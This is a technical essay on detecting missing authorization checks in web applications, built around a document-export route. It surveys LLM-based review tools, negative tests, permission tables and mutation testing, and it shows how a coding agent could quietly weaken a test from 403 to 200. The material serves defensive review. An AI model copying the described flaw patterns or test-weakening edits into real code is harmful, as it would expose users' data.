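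Teams can avoid investigating the same false alarm twice by recording intended exceptions, such as the route for shared links, with the reason and the name of whoever approved it. This record also needs protection, because a pull request that adds the export route to the list of exceptions has the same effect as one that deletes the team condition. The new entry appears in the diff, so a reviewer can ask for the reason before approving it.

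## Using language models to find missing checks

A language model can read the export route and the code around it, work out that documents belong to teams, and conclude that the route should refuse requests from people outside the team, without being given that rule. But models have been much better at noticing text that shouldn't be there than at noticing that text is missing, and the more successful tools avoid prompting them with the open question "is anything missing?"

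### Missing lines in a diff

In *AbsenceBench*, Fu, Shrivastava and colleagues (2025) gave models an original text and a copy with about a tenth of its lines deleted, and asked them to list the deleted lines. The texts were poems, sequences of numbers, and diffs with 10 to 200 changed lines from large GitHub projects. Claude 3.7 Sonnet did best of the 14 models tested on the diffs, with an F1 of 40.0%. It scored 96.0% on the number sequences, so it could follow the instructions.

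In a reversed version, three models had to find lines the researchers had added, and each scored at least 86.2% on the diffs. This exaggerates the contrast, because the added lines came from *Harry Potter*, and a sentence from a novel is much easier to spot in a diff than the mailing line would be.

Fu and colleagues suggest that the cause is attention, the mechanism that determines which parts of a text matter for a model's next step. Unlike an added line, a deleted line leaves nothing for the model to attend to. To test this, they put a marker reading "missing line" at each gap. On the diffs, the score of Claude 3.7 Sonnet without extra reasoning rose from 35.7% to 64.9%, and the scores of two other models rose from around 30% to 46.8%. The result fits the explanation, but the markers also showed where to look and how many lines were gone, which would help even if attention were not the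 cause.

These models are several generations old, so their scores are not a guide to how current models would perform. The task also differs from code review. The models had the complete text, so an ordinary file-comparison program could have found every missing line. A reviewer of the export route has no complete version to compare against and has to judge that the team condition is needed.

### Missing facts in clinical notes

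In 2026, Fox and colleagues tested models on omissions without giving them a complete version for comparison. A model read the transcript of a medical consultation and had to judge a note about it. The evaluation used 495 notes with one planted error each, along with clean versions of the same notes. The researchers had removed a fact from 293 of the notes with errors and had added or altered one in the other 202.

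The researchers tested eight setups by varying whether the prompt mentioned completeness, whether the model gave a yes-or-no answer or a score, and whether it judged each note once or eight times. They then measured how often the flawed note scored worse than its clean version, with ties counting as half, so guessing would give 0.5. This rate ranged from 0.79 to 0.94 for added or altered facts and from 0.50 to 0.63 for omissions.

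In ordinary use there is no clean version to compare with, so the model has to judge each note on its own. Two of the eight designs flagged 40% to 42% of the notes with omissions, but they also flagged 32% of the perfect notes. Rewording the prompt, taking votes and running an automatic prompt optimiser mostly changed how often the model flagged notes, without making it much better at distinguishing notes with omissions from perfect ones.

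All eight designs used a GPT model with its reasoning turned off. A Gemini model, tested with two of the prompts, also did worse on omissions, scoring 0.55 and 0.68 on them compared with 0.95 and 0.96 on added or altered facts. Extra reasoning helped the GPT model with both omissions and additions, so the gap did not close.

Changing the task helped more. In this version, a model first lists the important facts in the transcript without seeing the note. It then answers, for each fact, whether the note contains it. These are the results for 131 omissions that the researchers had set aside for a final test:

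| How the model judged the note | Flawed note scored worse than clean note |
|---|---|
| One overall score | 0.570 |
| One overall score, with the list of facts | 0.634 |
| One overall score, with more reasoning | 0.670 |
| One overall score, with the list and more reasoning | 0.699 |
| A separate verdict on each fact | 0.786 |

The list alone accounted for about a third of the improvement from 0.570 to 0.786. The rest came from making the model give a separate answer for each fact.

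How a tool combines the answers also matters. A note missing one fact out of about 38 still has a high average, so Fox and colleagues flagged a note whenever it lacked any fact graded critical. On the set-aside notes, this rule found 20.6% of the omissions, while a cut-off on the average of the same answers found 7.6% at the same false-alarm rate. An overall security score for a pull request could hide a missing check in the same way.

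On the full set of notes, the rule found 24.6% of the omissions and flagged 2.7% of the clean notes. A single prompt that told the model to make the list and work through it, and gave it room to reason, found 36.9% of the omissions and flagged 6.2% of the clean notes. Both did worst when the note also stated the removed fact elsewhere, with the single prompt finding 4 of those 57 omissions and the rule finding none. Similarly, a team condition on the viewing route might mislead a model about the export route, though this study can't show that.

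The method starts by listing the facts in each transcript, as the researchers did when they built their test, so the test may have overstated how well the method works. The researchers reply that another fact-by-fact method, with its own prompts, separated the flawed notes from the clean ones about as well.

This approach is hard to apply to code mainly because a repository seldom lists the checks that each route needs, whereas a transcript contains the facts that a good note should include.

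### Working through an application route by route

ABSENTIA, the tool by Duarte and colleagues, has a model infer the expected checks from the application. It works in three steps:

1. **Map the routes.** An agent identifies the web framework, the databases and the login system, and works out whether the application grants access by ownership, by role or by both. Two more agents write search patterns for this application's routes, inputs, permission checks and database queries. A program runs the patterns and records the file and line of each match, grouped by route.
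2. **Infer what each route must guarantee.** An agent takes one route, reads its code, follows the calls into other files, and states in plain language the properties that should hold. It then looks for the code that enforces each one.
3. **Try to break each guarantee.** The agent describes a request that the route would accept and the property forbids. If it can, the tool reports the property, the relevant lines, the request and its effect.

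For the export route, the agent would read the `Document` class, see that every document has a `team_id`, and might write the guarantee "only members of a document's team can export it". It would find no line that enforces this guarantee. It could then describe a request that breaks it, such as a user in team 3 asking to export document 12, which belongs to team 5. The agent doesn't send the request, because ABSENTIA only reads source code.

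A last stage looks for pairs of routes that are harmless separately but unsafe together. This stage wasn't needed to find any of the known flaws in the benchmark.

The 30 disclosed flaws in the benchmark come from 25 open-source applications, which have a median of 220 routes. ABSENTIA found 19 of the flaws, while CodeQL and Semgrep found none. ABSENTIA stopped reporting 17 of the 19 once the developers had fixed them. It still reported the other two in the repaired code, so it had probably not identified the actual problem.

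An agent that used the same model, but was simply told to audit the whole application, found 3. It could take up to 200 steps but used 59 on average, and in 24 of the 30 runs it stopped because it considered itself finished. Duarte and colleagues added the parts of their method one at a time to see which ones helped:

| Method | Known flaws found | Reports per run | Reports confirmed by another model |
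|---|---|---|---|
| Undirected agent | 3 of 30 | 6 | 73.6% |
| One route at a time | 18 of 30 | 119 | 40.5% |
| One route at a time, with stated guarantees and requests that break them | 19 of 30 | 77 | 50.8% |

Nearly all the gain came from making the model look at every route. The third step found only one more flaw, which could be chance, but it cut the number of reports by a third. It is unclear whether the remaining reports were more accurate. A security researcher on the team judged 73 reports without knowing which method had produced them, and confirmed 42% of those from the full method and 43% of those from the simpler one.

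Of the 11 flaws that ABSENTIA missed, three were in routes that the map had left out, so no agent read them. An agent read the routes containing the other eight but did not report the flaws. The tool ran on MiniMax-2.5, a model that companies can run on their own machines. When Claude Sonnet 5 read the same 27 mapped routes, it reported 22 flaws, compared with 19 for MiniMax-2.5, a difference small enough to be chance. It still missed the three flaws in the unmapped routes.

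Results also vary between runs. The researchers ran ABSENTIA five times on each of the eight smallest applications. For six of them, the result for the known flaw was the same every time, and for the other two it changed. A clean result from one run is therefore weak evidence that a route is safe.

### Making the model prove that a check exists

A model that reads every route can still accept a check that doesn't work. *Suspected Until Inspected* (Yang, Kang and colleagues, 2026) describes a case from a business-intelligence application. Before deleting an access token, the code checked whether the user was allowed to delete it. But the check treated the user as the token's owner, without reading the stored token to see who owned it, so it approved everyone. The model found no flaw when asked to audit the code, and when asked whether the deletion was restricted, it cited the check.

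Their tool, FLINT, doesn't let the model decide whether a route is safe. For each route, the model lists the stored objects that the request selects, each place where the code reads or changes them, and every line that restricts who may do so. An ordinary program then examines those lines. It accepts a check only if:

- the line exists and compares or tests something about the current user;
- it concerns the object that the route uses, and not some other object;
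- a failed check stops the request, or keeps other people's records out of the query;
- it is strong enough for the operation, so permission to read does not allow deletion;
- it applies on every path to the operation.

If an operation has no accepted check, FLINT reports it. For the export route, the model would list the operation that reads the document but no restriction on it. For the route whose team condition was loosened, the model might cite `current_user.is_logged_in`, which the program should reject because the condition doesn't involve the document. The model's belief that the code is safe doesn't affect either result. FLINT also tells the model which operations are unguarded and lets it cite another line for each, which the program checks in the same way.

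The weak point is the first list. If the model leaves out an operation, later steps won't examine it, so the problem of noticing what is missing remains, but at an earlier step.

Yang and colleagues compared FLINT with other methods on 69 routes, each in a vulnerable version and a repaired version. All the methods in this table used the same model, DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash, and the percentages are averages over 35 repositories:

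| Method | Flagged the vulnerable version | Flagged the repaired version | Flagged only the vulnerable version |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model audits the route directly | 46.7% | 11.1% | 36.7% |
| Model lists operations and checks, and the tool believes most of them | 71.0% | 36.9% | 38.8% |
| FLINT | 85.2% | 27.2% | 62.8% |
| Codex CLI, a coding agent | 97.1% | 22.9% | 74.3% |
| Claude Code, a coding agent | 91.9% | 12.3% | 79.6% |

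The second row shows that listing the checks hardly helped the model tell vulnerable code from repaired code, but verifying the listed checks did help. The two coding agents did better still, without a certificate or a verifier. They could read the whole repository, and their instructions specified which route to examine. Claude Code cost four to five times as much per route as FLINT.

FLINT also did better on 41 flaws that the researchers had discovered themselves. It pointed to the operation at fault in 28 of them, compared with 21 for Claude Code and 23 for Codex CLI. That set may favour FLINT, because the researchers ran the tool on these collections while developing it. The method also depends heavily on the model. With the larger DeepSeek-V4-Pro, it distinguished only 29.6% of the pairs, partly because that model more often listed no operations.

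The study also tested weakened checks. The researchers altered each of 33 real fixes so that the original attack worked again, for example by requiring a lesser permission or by recording a failed check without stopping the request. Of the 31 cases that every method completed, the direct audit flagged 14, FLINT 24, Claude Code 27 and Codex CLI 30. The differences between FLINT and the two agents could be chance, but all three flagged many of the weakened checks.

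Researchers used FLINT to search 57 popular applications and found 112 previously unknown flaws, each of which they confirmed on their own copy of the application. In 40 cases the code had no check, and in 41 it checked the wrong object. The presence of a check is therefore a poor reason to approve a route.

### The line after the gap

Rahman, Akil and colleagues (2026), in *SPLASH*, measure where a model would have written something else, instead of asking it for a list.

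The model receives a finished program with two sets of instructions. One asks it to review the code for security, and the other asks it to review the code for readability and style. In each case, it should return the code unchanged if nothing needs fixing. SPLASH doesn't let the model write a reply. It takes the existing program piece by piece and records how probable the model considers each piece as the next part of its answer. (The pieces, called tokens, are words or parts of words.) The score for a token is:

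pressure = log(probability in the style review) − log(probability in the security review)

Suppose the model has read the line that fetches the document in the export route, and the next token is `return`. The model gives this token a probability of 0.8 in the style review but only 0.1 in the security review, because there it predicts a condition first. With these invented figures, the pressure is log(0.8/0.1), or about 2.1. SPLASH adds up the positive scores for each statement and ranks the statements. The missing condition has no line of its own, but it raises the score of the line after the gap.

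This approach deals with the problem that Fu and colleagues identified because it gives the missing check a position in the text, but it works only if the model expects a check there. A model that is given only the export route, with no sign that documents belong to teams, has little reason to expect the team condition. Rahman and colleagues report that every method that judged the code did poorly when the security tests enforced a requirement the task had not stated.

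The evaluation of SPLASH used short programs that 12 models had written for 899 tasks. When a model's working attempts at a task included both secure and insecure programs, SPLASH picked a secure one 74% of the time, compared with 54% for a random choice. Asking the same reviewing model whether each program was vulnerable, and using the probability of "yes", did just as well, but SPLASH has the advantage of also pointing to a line. It ranked the vulnerable statement first in 58% of insecure programs and in the top three in 85%. In programs with 36 or more statements, it ranked the vulnerable statement first only 29% of the time.

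These location figures are limited evidence about missing checks. The researchers used warnings from static analysis tools to decide which statements were vulnerable, and those tools often can't detect a missing check. The researchers acknowledge that such flaws are underrepresented. In a second test, which used pairs of secure and insecure programs, SPLASH identified the exact changed line in 77% of pairs. But the researchers counted lines that the secure version replaced or deleted, so a fix that only added a check would leave no line for SPLASH to identify.

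SPLASH is best suited to choosing among several versions of the same code or suggesting where to start reading. Its scores aren't comparable between tasks, so they can't show whether a particular pull request is safe.

### Do specific questions help?

The clinical-notes method, ABSENTIA and FLINT all replace "is anything missing?" with narrower questions, such as whether a note mentions a particular allergy, what a route must guarantee, or which line stops other users from accessing a record. A model can answer these by looking for something that is present, and a blank answer shows where something may be missing. A reviewer who writes down the expected checks before opening a diff does the same.

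The results support some parts of this idea more than others. They give good support to making the model cover everything, since the undirected agent found 3 flaws and a route-by-route search with the same model found 18. The coding agents' success in the FLINT study also fits, because they didn't need a more elaborate method once someone had told them which route to read. The two studies used different models and different flaws, so this comparison is only suggestive.

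Good evidence also supports answering each question separately. In the clinical notes, giving a separate verdict on each question improved detection more than the list did. In the FLINT study, a list of checks helped mainly when a program verified it. The exact form of the question may not matter much. In ABSENTIA, stating guarantees and forbidden requests reduced the number of reports but uncovered only one more flaw.

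Giving a model a long checklist to work through in a single answer can make it less accurate. In a pilot for *Trusting the Tool* (2026), Liu and Gao asked a model to judge 30 pairs of vulnerable and repaired C functions. It judged both versions correctly in 10 pairs without a checklist, but in only 5 or 6 when the prompt presented facts from a static analysis tool as a checklist. The score fell because the model called more functions safe after working through the items. The pilot tested only one older model on 30 pairs, but people who tick boxes on a checklist may make a similar mistake.

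Models may not need special help to find familiar omissions. In *Broken by Default* (2026), Blain and Noiseux asked models to review the security of 89 flawed programs that the same models had written. Many of the programs calculated how much memory to reserve without checking whether the number had become too large. The models recognised 70 of them (79%) as vulnerable. The test included no sound programs, so a model that called everything vulnerable would have scored 100%. A missing overflow check is a textbook flaw, unlike the missing team condition.

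### Auditing an application and reviewing one change

ABSENTIA is meant for auditing a whole application. It produced 77 reports per run and gave most of them its highest confidence, so they were not usefully ranked. A security team might accept this once or twice a year, but someone reviewing a single pull request could not.

FLINT ranks its reports but has the same difficulty. In five complete applications, it produced at least one definite finding for 49% of the 786 request-handling functions. The researchers read the 24 reports in which the model's output both acknowledged the flaw and described an attack. Eight described real or plausible flaws, seven described flaws with little impact, and nine were false positives.

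Reviewing one change requires fewer questions, because the tool can start from the routes that the change adds or affects and skip the rest. ABSENTIA does something similar when it runs again after a commit. It keeps its earlier result for a route if the files behind that route and the files they import are all unchanged, and it analyses the other routes again. Checking the imported files also lets it catch indirect effects.

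Duarte and colleagues tested this by treating each repaired version as the old code and the vulnerable version as the new, as if a commit had undone the fix. ABSENTIA reported 21 of the 30 known flaws, but the researchers did not count how many other reports it made.

The saving was also uneven. In the median case, ABSENTIA could reuse its verdicts for 37% of the routes. In nine cases it reused at least 70%, but in eight it reused none, because the commit had touched a file that most of the application depended on. At about $0.20 a route, a full audit of an application with 220 routes would cost $44, and auditing it again after a typical commit would cost about $28, which is a lot for every small pull request.

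It may be cheaper to give a coding agent the name of each new or changed route and let it search the repository. The FLINT study suggests that agents do this well, but half of the versions in its test set contained a flaw. Most pull requests don't, so a larger share of an agent's reports would be false alarms in practice. Suppose, for illustration, that a project adds 100 routes in a year and five lack a check they need. An agent with Claude Code's rates in that study would flag about five of the unsafe routes and, if it misjudged ordinary routes as often as repaired ones, about 12 of the 95 safe ones. Fewer than a third of its reports would be right, but a reviewer could check 17 reports in a year without much trouble.

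A prompt for the export route might read as follows. It is a suggestion based on these methods, and none of the studies tested it:

```text
Examine GET /documents/<doc_id>/export. You may read any file.
1. From the data model and the other routes that return documents,
   work out who should be able to receive this document.
2. Give the file and line that refuses everyone else before the
   document is returned. If you cannot find one, say so.
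3. Describe a request that this route accepts and that the rule
   in step 1 forbids, or explain why there is none.
```

The reviewer should open the line that the model cites, since FLINT doesn't rely on the model's answer alone either. If the answer to the second step is blank, the reviewer has a specific question for the author. When a pull request removes or loosens a check, the prompt can quote the old condition so that the model doesn't have to infer the rule. Asking about each route separately is safer than asking once about the whole pull request, because a model that has found the condition on one route might not notice that another route lacks it.

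### Descriptions and earlier verdicts

Information accompanying code can change a model's verdict on it. In *Words Speak Louder Than Code*, Shahriar, Cai and colleagues (2026) found that all eight models they tested reached different verdicts on identical code depending on the author's reputation, the wording of the task or the result of an earlier analysis. The effect was generally larger for flaws that require reasoning about what the code means. For missing checks, false reassurance is a greater danger than false alarms. Liu and Gao found that notes wrongly stating that a check existed lowered detection by up to 19 percentage points, while false alarms never significantly lowered accuracy.

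The model should therefore judge the code before it reads the pull request's description, the author's name or another tool's verdict. Comments can also mislead it, and SPLASH removes them before it scores a program. The reviewer can then ask the model, in a separate request, to confirm against the code each statement that a check exists, such as "access already checked upstream". When Liu and Gao did this and showed the model which statements had failed, one model regained 12 points of accuracy. A second model gained about half as much, which could have been due to chance.

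## Testing whether a missing check would be caught

Instructions, tools and language models can all lead a reviewer to suspect that a check is missing. The reviewer can find out by running a test that makes the forbidden request and passes only if the program refuses it. Most existing tests, however, only confirm that permitted actions work. The owner's export test, for example, passes with or without the team condition.

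That test also runs every line of the export route. A coverage tool, which reports the share of lines that a project's tests run, would therefore show 100% for the route. The missing condition can't lower the figure because it has no line to count.

### Negative tests

A negative test confirms that the program refuses a forbidden action. For the export route, it can be the owner's test with a different login and a different expected result:

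```python
def test_other_team_cannot_export():
    log_in(user_from_another_team)
    assert get("/documents/7/export").status_code == 403
```

This test fails on the export route, which returns the document with status code 200. *Transforming and selecting functional test cases for security policy testing* describes tools that adapt a Java program's existing tests in a similar way.

The test has to send a request that would succeed if the check were absent. *Model-Based Tests for Access Control Policies*, by Pretschner, Mouelhi and Le Traon, gives an example from a library system that forbids borrowers to return books on maintenance days. The test has a student borrow a book, sets the date to a maintenance day and then tries to return the book. It passes only if the program reports a breach of the security policy. Without the first step, the program might reject the return because the student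 had never borrowed the book. Likewise, document 7 must exist, and the test should pass only on error 403. If it accepted any error, it would pass whenever the export feature crashed.

### A permission table for the document application

Suppose that each team in the document application has a manager, who alone may delete the team's documents. As before, anyone with a secret link may read the document it leads to. Four kinds of user and five routes give 20 expected outcomes:

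| Route | Visitor, not logged in | User from another team | Member of the document's team | Manager of that team |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| View | 403 | 403 | 200 | 200 |
| Export | 403 | 403 | 200 | 200 |
| Rename | 403 | 403 | 200 | 200 |
| Delete | 403 | 403 | 403 | 200 |
| Open by secret link | 200 | 200 | 200 | 200 |

The nine cells with 403 are negative tests. The other 11 check that permitted users still get in, because a route that refused everyone would pass all nine negative tests.

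The example changes from earlier make different cells fail:

| Change | Cells that fail |
|---|---|
| Team condition deleted from the viewing route | View: visitor and user from another team |
| Team condition loosened to any logged-in user | View: user from another team |
| Export route added without the team condition | Export: visitor and user from another team, if the table has an export row |
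| Line added that emails each document to an outsider | None |

Tests that cover only owners and visitors would not catch the loosened condition, so the table also needs a user from another team. Unlike a missing check, the mailing line is easy for a reviewer to see, but all 20 tests pass because it doesn't change any response code.

OWASP's *Authorization Testing Automation Cheat Sheet* recommends keeping such a table in a file and running the tests from it. Its sample has three roles and four services. One test per role calls every service and compares the response with the table. Roles alone wouldn't be enough for the document application, because members of the owning team and of other teams are all ordinary users. OWASP mentions data as a third dimension for rules of this kind.

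According to the same guidance, most authorization problems arise when an update adds or changes a feature and nobody works out the effect on permissions. Yet the sample tests loop over the services in the file, so they would never call a route that nobody had listed. If the document table had no export row, the remaining 16 tests would pass. One more test can close this gap by comparing the table with the routes that the application really has:

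```python
def test_table_covers_every_route():
    routes = {rule.endpoint for rule in app.url_map.iter_rules()}
    assert routes == set(PERMISSIONS)
```

Flask, a Python web framework, lists its routes this way. The `PERMISSIONS` table has one entry per route, including public ones. The pull request that adds the export route now fails until someone adds a row for it. If the author writes 403 for a user from another team, that test will fail and they will find the missing condition. If they write 200, the tests pass, but the diff now contains a line that lists other teams as allowed to export the document, and a reviewer can object to it.

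### Deleting one check at a time

Mutation testing measures whether a test suite would catch a missing check, which a passing run doesn't show. A tool makes one small change to the code, producing a "mutant", and runs the tests. If any test fails, the mutant is "killed"; if they all pass, it survives. The mutation score is the number of mutants killed divided by the number made. To apply this to security, the tool deletes or loosens one check at a time.

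The viewing route could have two mutants, one that deletes the team condition and one that loosens it to allow any logged-in user. If the only negative test uses a visitor who isn't logged in, it kills the first mutant but not the second, for a score of 50%. A test with a logged-in user from another team kills both.

Hill (2026), in *Four Ways to Forge a Bundle My Own Verifier Calls Clean*, tried this on a program that checks whether a published claim's evidence files support it. Hill disabled the program's 112 statements that reject bad submissions, one at a time, and for 75 of them no test in the suite failed. The project also had 16 deliberately corrupted submissions, kept to prove that the program could reject bad ones. On their own, these caught 10 of the 112 disabled statements.

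Hill had manually found four ways to get a false submission accepted. Fixing all four and adding a corrupted submission for each moved the score only from 37 of 112 to 39 of 119, because the fixes added seven new rejection statements, five of which were untested. Hill then wrote 75 tests, one for each statement that had survived at the start, and the score rose to 112 of 119. Some of that rise was guaranteed because the tests targeted those statements. Even so, a team that adds a test only after each incident will probably leave most of its other checks unprotected.

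The score also fell from 100% to 97% when a new feature added 12 rejection statements. Projects therefore need to repeat the measurement, which is quick for a program of this size. A later run with 143 mutants took under six minutes.

Hill's figures come from one program, which Hill wrote and measured alone, but the study documents two problems that anyone using mutation testing could have. In one run the score was a perfect 119 of 119 because some tests were already failing before any deletion, so every mutant counted as killed. The tests must pass on the unchanged code first. The second problem is more serious for reviewers, because deleting existing statements can't reveal a check that was never written, and one of the four forgeries worked for that reason. Mutation testing can show that tests protect the viewing route's condition, but the export route has no condition to delete, so only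 the permission table covers that case.

A surviving mutant doesn't always mean there is a gap in the tests. If a central check also refuses outsiders, deleting the route's own condition doesn't change who gets access, so no test could fail.

### Mutating access rules

Some applications keep their access rules in a separate policy file, and researchers have mutated those files directly. Martin and Xie (2006), in *Automated Mutation Testing of Access Control Policies*, altered 11 policies by removing rules, making conditions always true, swapping "permit" and "deny", and similar edits. They then compared three sets of test requests:

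| Test requests | Average share of mutants killed |
|---|---|
| Generated by a tool to reach particular rules | 59% |
| 50 random requests per policy | 47% |
| The fewest random requests that kept the same coverage | 38% |

For most policies, these requests reached all or nearly all of the rules, but many altered rules still went undetected. Discarding requests that added no coverage made detection worse. The random requests missed one policy entirely, which lowered their averages. Removing a whole rule was among the easiest changes to detect, with detection rates of at least 90%. Changes to how the policy resolves conflicts between rules were the hardest, with rates under 11%.

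Pretschner and colleagues used mutation to find out which tests are worth keeping when there are too many combinations to try. They mutated the policies of a library, a hospital, an auction site and a meeting system, which each had between 280 and 736 combinations of role, permission and circumstance. One test per rule used only about 17% of the combinations and did better than the same number of random tests in three of the four systems. They could not explain why so few tests did so well, and they declined to generalise from four policies. The document application doesn't need a selection of tests, because a computer can make 20 requests in seconds.

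When the checks are in ordinary code, the choice of mutants matters. In *Towards Security-aware Mutation Testing*, Loise, Devroey and colleagues designed 15 kinds of security mutant for Java, such as removing the code that cleans file names or replacing an input filter with one that accepts everything. On a medical-records application, a standard mutation tool made 5,486 mutants, and a security scanner found new vulnerabilities in two. The security mutants produced 62. But these counts include only what the scanner could recognise. The standard tool had also removed hundreds of conditions, and if some of those were authorization checks, the scanner would probably have missed their removal.

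A reviewer can do a small version of this by hand. When a pull request adds or moves a check, the reviewer deletes the check in a private copy and runs the tests. If they all pass, the reviewer can ask for a negative test before approving.

### Reading the tests before the code

Alphabetical file order usually puts tests last. In the test-first experiment mentioned earlier, from *Test-Driven Code Review* (Spadini, Palomba and colleagues, 2019), 92 developers reviewed changes to a small Java game with planted bugs and maintainability problems, such as misleading names. Some saw the tests first and others the production code (the program itself), but all could switch between the two.

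| Share found | Tests first | Production code first |
|---|---|---|
| Bugs in production code | 28% | 33% |
| Bugs in tests | 40% | 17% |
| Maintainability problems in production code | 8% | 21% |

The difference for production bugs could easily be chance, but the other two differences were statistically significant. The gain in the tests therefore came with more overlooked maintainability problems in the code. Review times were similar.

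None of the planted bugs was a missing security check, but reading the tests first may still help a reviewer find one, because the reviewer can quickly see which users the tests log in as. If every test of the export route logs in as a team member, no test checks whether the route refuses anyone else. An author who makes a mistaken assumption in the code can also repeat it in the tests, so it seems safer to list the expected refusals first, compare the tests with that list, and then read the code.

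In a survey of 103 developers by Spadini and colleagues, only 18 said they always or almost always start a review with the tests. Several respondents said that production code matters more, or that tests are often too poor to learn from.

### When an agent edits the tests as well

A permission table protects the team condition only if the same pull request doesn't also change the table. A coding agent told to make all tests pass could do so with this edit:

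```diff
-    ("show_document", "other_team"): 403,
+    ("show_document", "other_team"): 200,
```

This is a weakened check in the test suite. As with a weakened check in the program, the reviewer should ask who decided that other teams may read the document.

In merged pull requests, agents seem to add tests more often than they alter or remove them. *Testing with Coding Agents* (Milanese, Salzano and colleagues, 2026) compared 114,134 merged pull requests from 391 Java projects. After adjusting for size, pull requests involving an agent had higher odds of adding tests than human-written ones (odds ratios of 1.50 to 1.58) and lower odds of deleting them (0.51 to 0.77). This is mildly reassuring, but the study didn't record whether the deleted tests had protected a security check.

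New tests can also do harm. Charoosaei, Richter and Papadakis (2026), in *On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing*, planted faults in 145 pull requests to three Python projects and had a language model write tests from the faulty code. Depending on the project, 8% to 17% of the tests passed on the faulty code and failed on the correct code. Only 2.4% to 4.8% did the opposite and revealed the fault. That share may be even lower in practice, because the researchers kept some failing tests that existing test generators would have discarded. The planted faults were small artificial edits, not missing security checks.

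On the export route, a model might log in as an outsider, receive the document and write a test that expects status code 200. When someone later adds the team condition, that test will fail and make the fix look like a bug. In the experiment, 83% to 91% of such tests still enforced the faulty behavior after several later commits.

Agents also use mocks, which are stand-ins for real components, more often. According to *Are Coding Agents Generating Over-Mocked Tests?* (2026), 36% of agents' commits that touched tests added mocks, compared with 26% of other test commits. If a test replaces the permission check with a mock that always approves, deleting the real check won't make the test fail.

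Reviewers also cannot count on a project's existing tests. *Test Coverage Analysis of Agentic Pull Requests* (2026) found that existing tests ran 61.5% of the lines agents changed in Java projects and 27.0% in Python projects.

Test changes therefore need a review of their own. This command shows them separately, if the project keeps its tests in one folder:

```text
git diff main...cleanup -- tests/
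```

The reviewer looks for deleted or skipped tests, tests whose expected response has changed from 403 to 200, and tests that now log in as a member instead of an outsider. Running the main branch's tests against the new code is a stronger safeguard, because edits to the tests can't affect the result. Some old tests will fail for good reasons, but the author should explain each failure. Automatic checks for deletions in agents' changes could also cover the test files.

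### Practice changes for reviewers

A team can test its reviewers in much the same way, by planting flaws in practice changes and counting how many people report them. This would also allow a direct comparison between missing checks and inserted malicious code, which existing reviewer experiments lack.

Each practice change could have three versions. For an export feature, these might be:

- a clean version with the team condition;
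- a version with a seeded omission, which leaves the condition out;
- a version with the condition and a seeded addition, such as the line that emails the document to `outsider.example`.

The addition is harmless because nobody can receive mail at that address, which is reserved for examples. The changes should still stay in a separate copy of the project that nobody can release. Reviewers should know that the team runs such exercises, and each should see only one version of a given change, chosen at random. Running the permission table first will confirm that omitting the check lets outsiders in.

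The team also has to decide in advance what counts as finding a flaw. Spadini and colleagues counted a comment only if it was in the right place and correctly identified the problem, and a second researcher reclassified the comments to verify the results.

### How many reviews the comparison needs

Suppose that reviewers really detect 65% of seeded additions and 45% of seeded omissions. With ten reviews of each kind, chance could easily hide or reverse the difference. The usual aim is 80% power, meaning an 80% probability that the exercise detects a true difference of this size, with a 5% risk of reporting a difference when there is none. A standard formula gives the number of reviews needed of each kind:

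n = (1.96 + 0.84)² × (0.65 × 0.35 + 0.45 × 0.55) / (0.65 − 0.45)² ≈ 93.1

The 1.96 comes from the 5% significance level and the 0.84 from 80% power. Rounding up gives 94 reviews of each kind, or 188 in total, plus the reviews of clean versions. A team of ten who each did one practice review a week would need about 19 weeks for the 188. Halving the difference roughly quadruples the number of reviews, so telling 65% from 55% would take about 373 of each kind.

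The formula assumes that the reviews are independent, which they won't be if ten people do 19 each. One sharp-eyed reviewer would influence many results, so the team would need an analysis that allows for differences between people, and perhaps more reviews. The team should also plant many different flaws. If all 94 omissions were the same missing team condition, the result would apply only to that flaw. The Java holiday experiment has the same limitation.

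### Sensitivity and willingness to flag

A reviewer who objects to every change will detect every flaw without showing any skill, so the team should also count how often reviewers object to the clean versions. Some clean versions should look suspicious, such as one with a route that seems unguarded but is covered by a central check, or one with a line that sends mail to an approved archiving service.

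Signal detection theory, which psychologists use to analyse such decisions, separates two quantities. Sensitivity is how well a reviewer distinguishes flawed changes from clean ones. Willingness to flag is how readily the reviewer objects when unsure. Let H be the share of flawed changes that a reviewer flags and F the share of clean ones:

sensitivity: d′ = z(H) − z(F)

willingness to flag: c = −(z(H) + z(F)) / 2

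The function z converts a percentage into a position on the normal curve, so z(50%) is 0, z(80%) is about 0.84 and z(20%) is about −0.84. A negative c means that the reviewer flags readily, and a positive c means that the reviewer holds back. Here are three invented reviewers:

| Reviewer | Flawed changes flagged | Clean changes flagged | d′ | c |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ana | 80% | 40% | 1.1 | −0.3 |
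| Ben | 60% | 20% | 1.1 | 0.3 |
| Chloe | 80% | 20% | 1.7 | 0 |

Ana detects more flaws than Ben, but only because she objects more often. Chloe is better than both at telling flawed changes from clean ones. Someone who flagged everything would have the same rate for flawed and clean changes, and so no sensitivity at all. (Rates of exactly 0% or 100% have no finite z, so analysts adjust them slightly before using the formula.)

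If a test shows that reviewers suspect missing checks but seldom mention them, encouraging them to ask could help. If they can't tell a guarded route from an unguarded one, encouragement will mostly produce more false alarms, and they need better information about the application's rules.

To compare omissions with additions, the team should also record whether each false alarm was about a missing check or malicious code. Reviewers might often ask for checks that already exist but rarely mistake an ordinary line for an attack. A single false-alarm rate would then overstate how well they notice omissions compared with additions.
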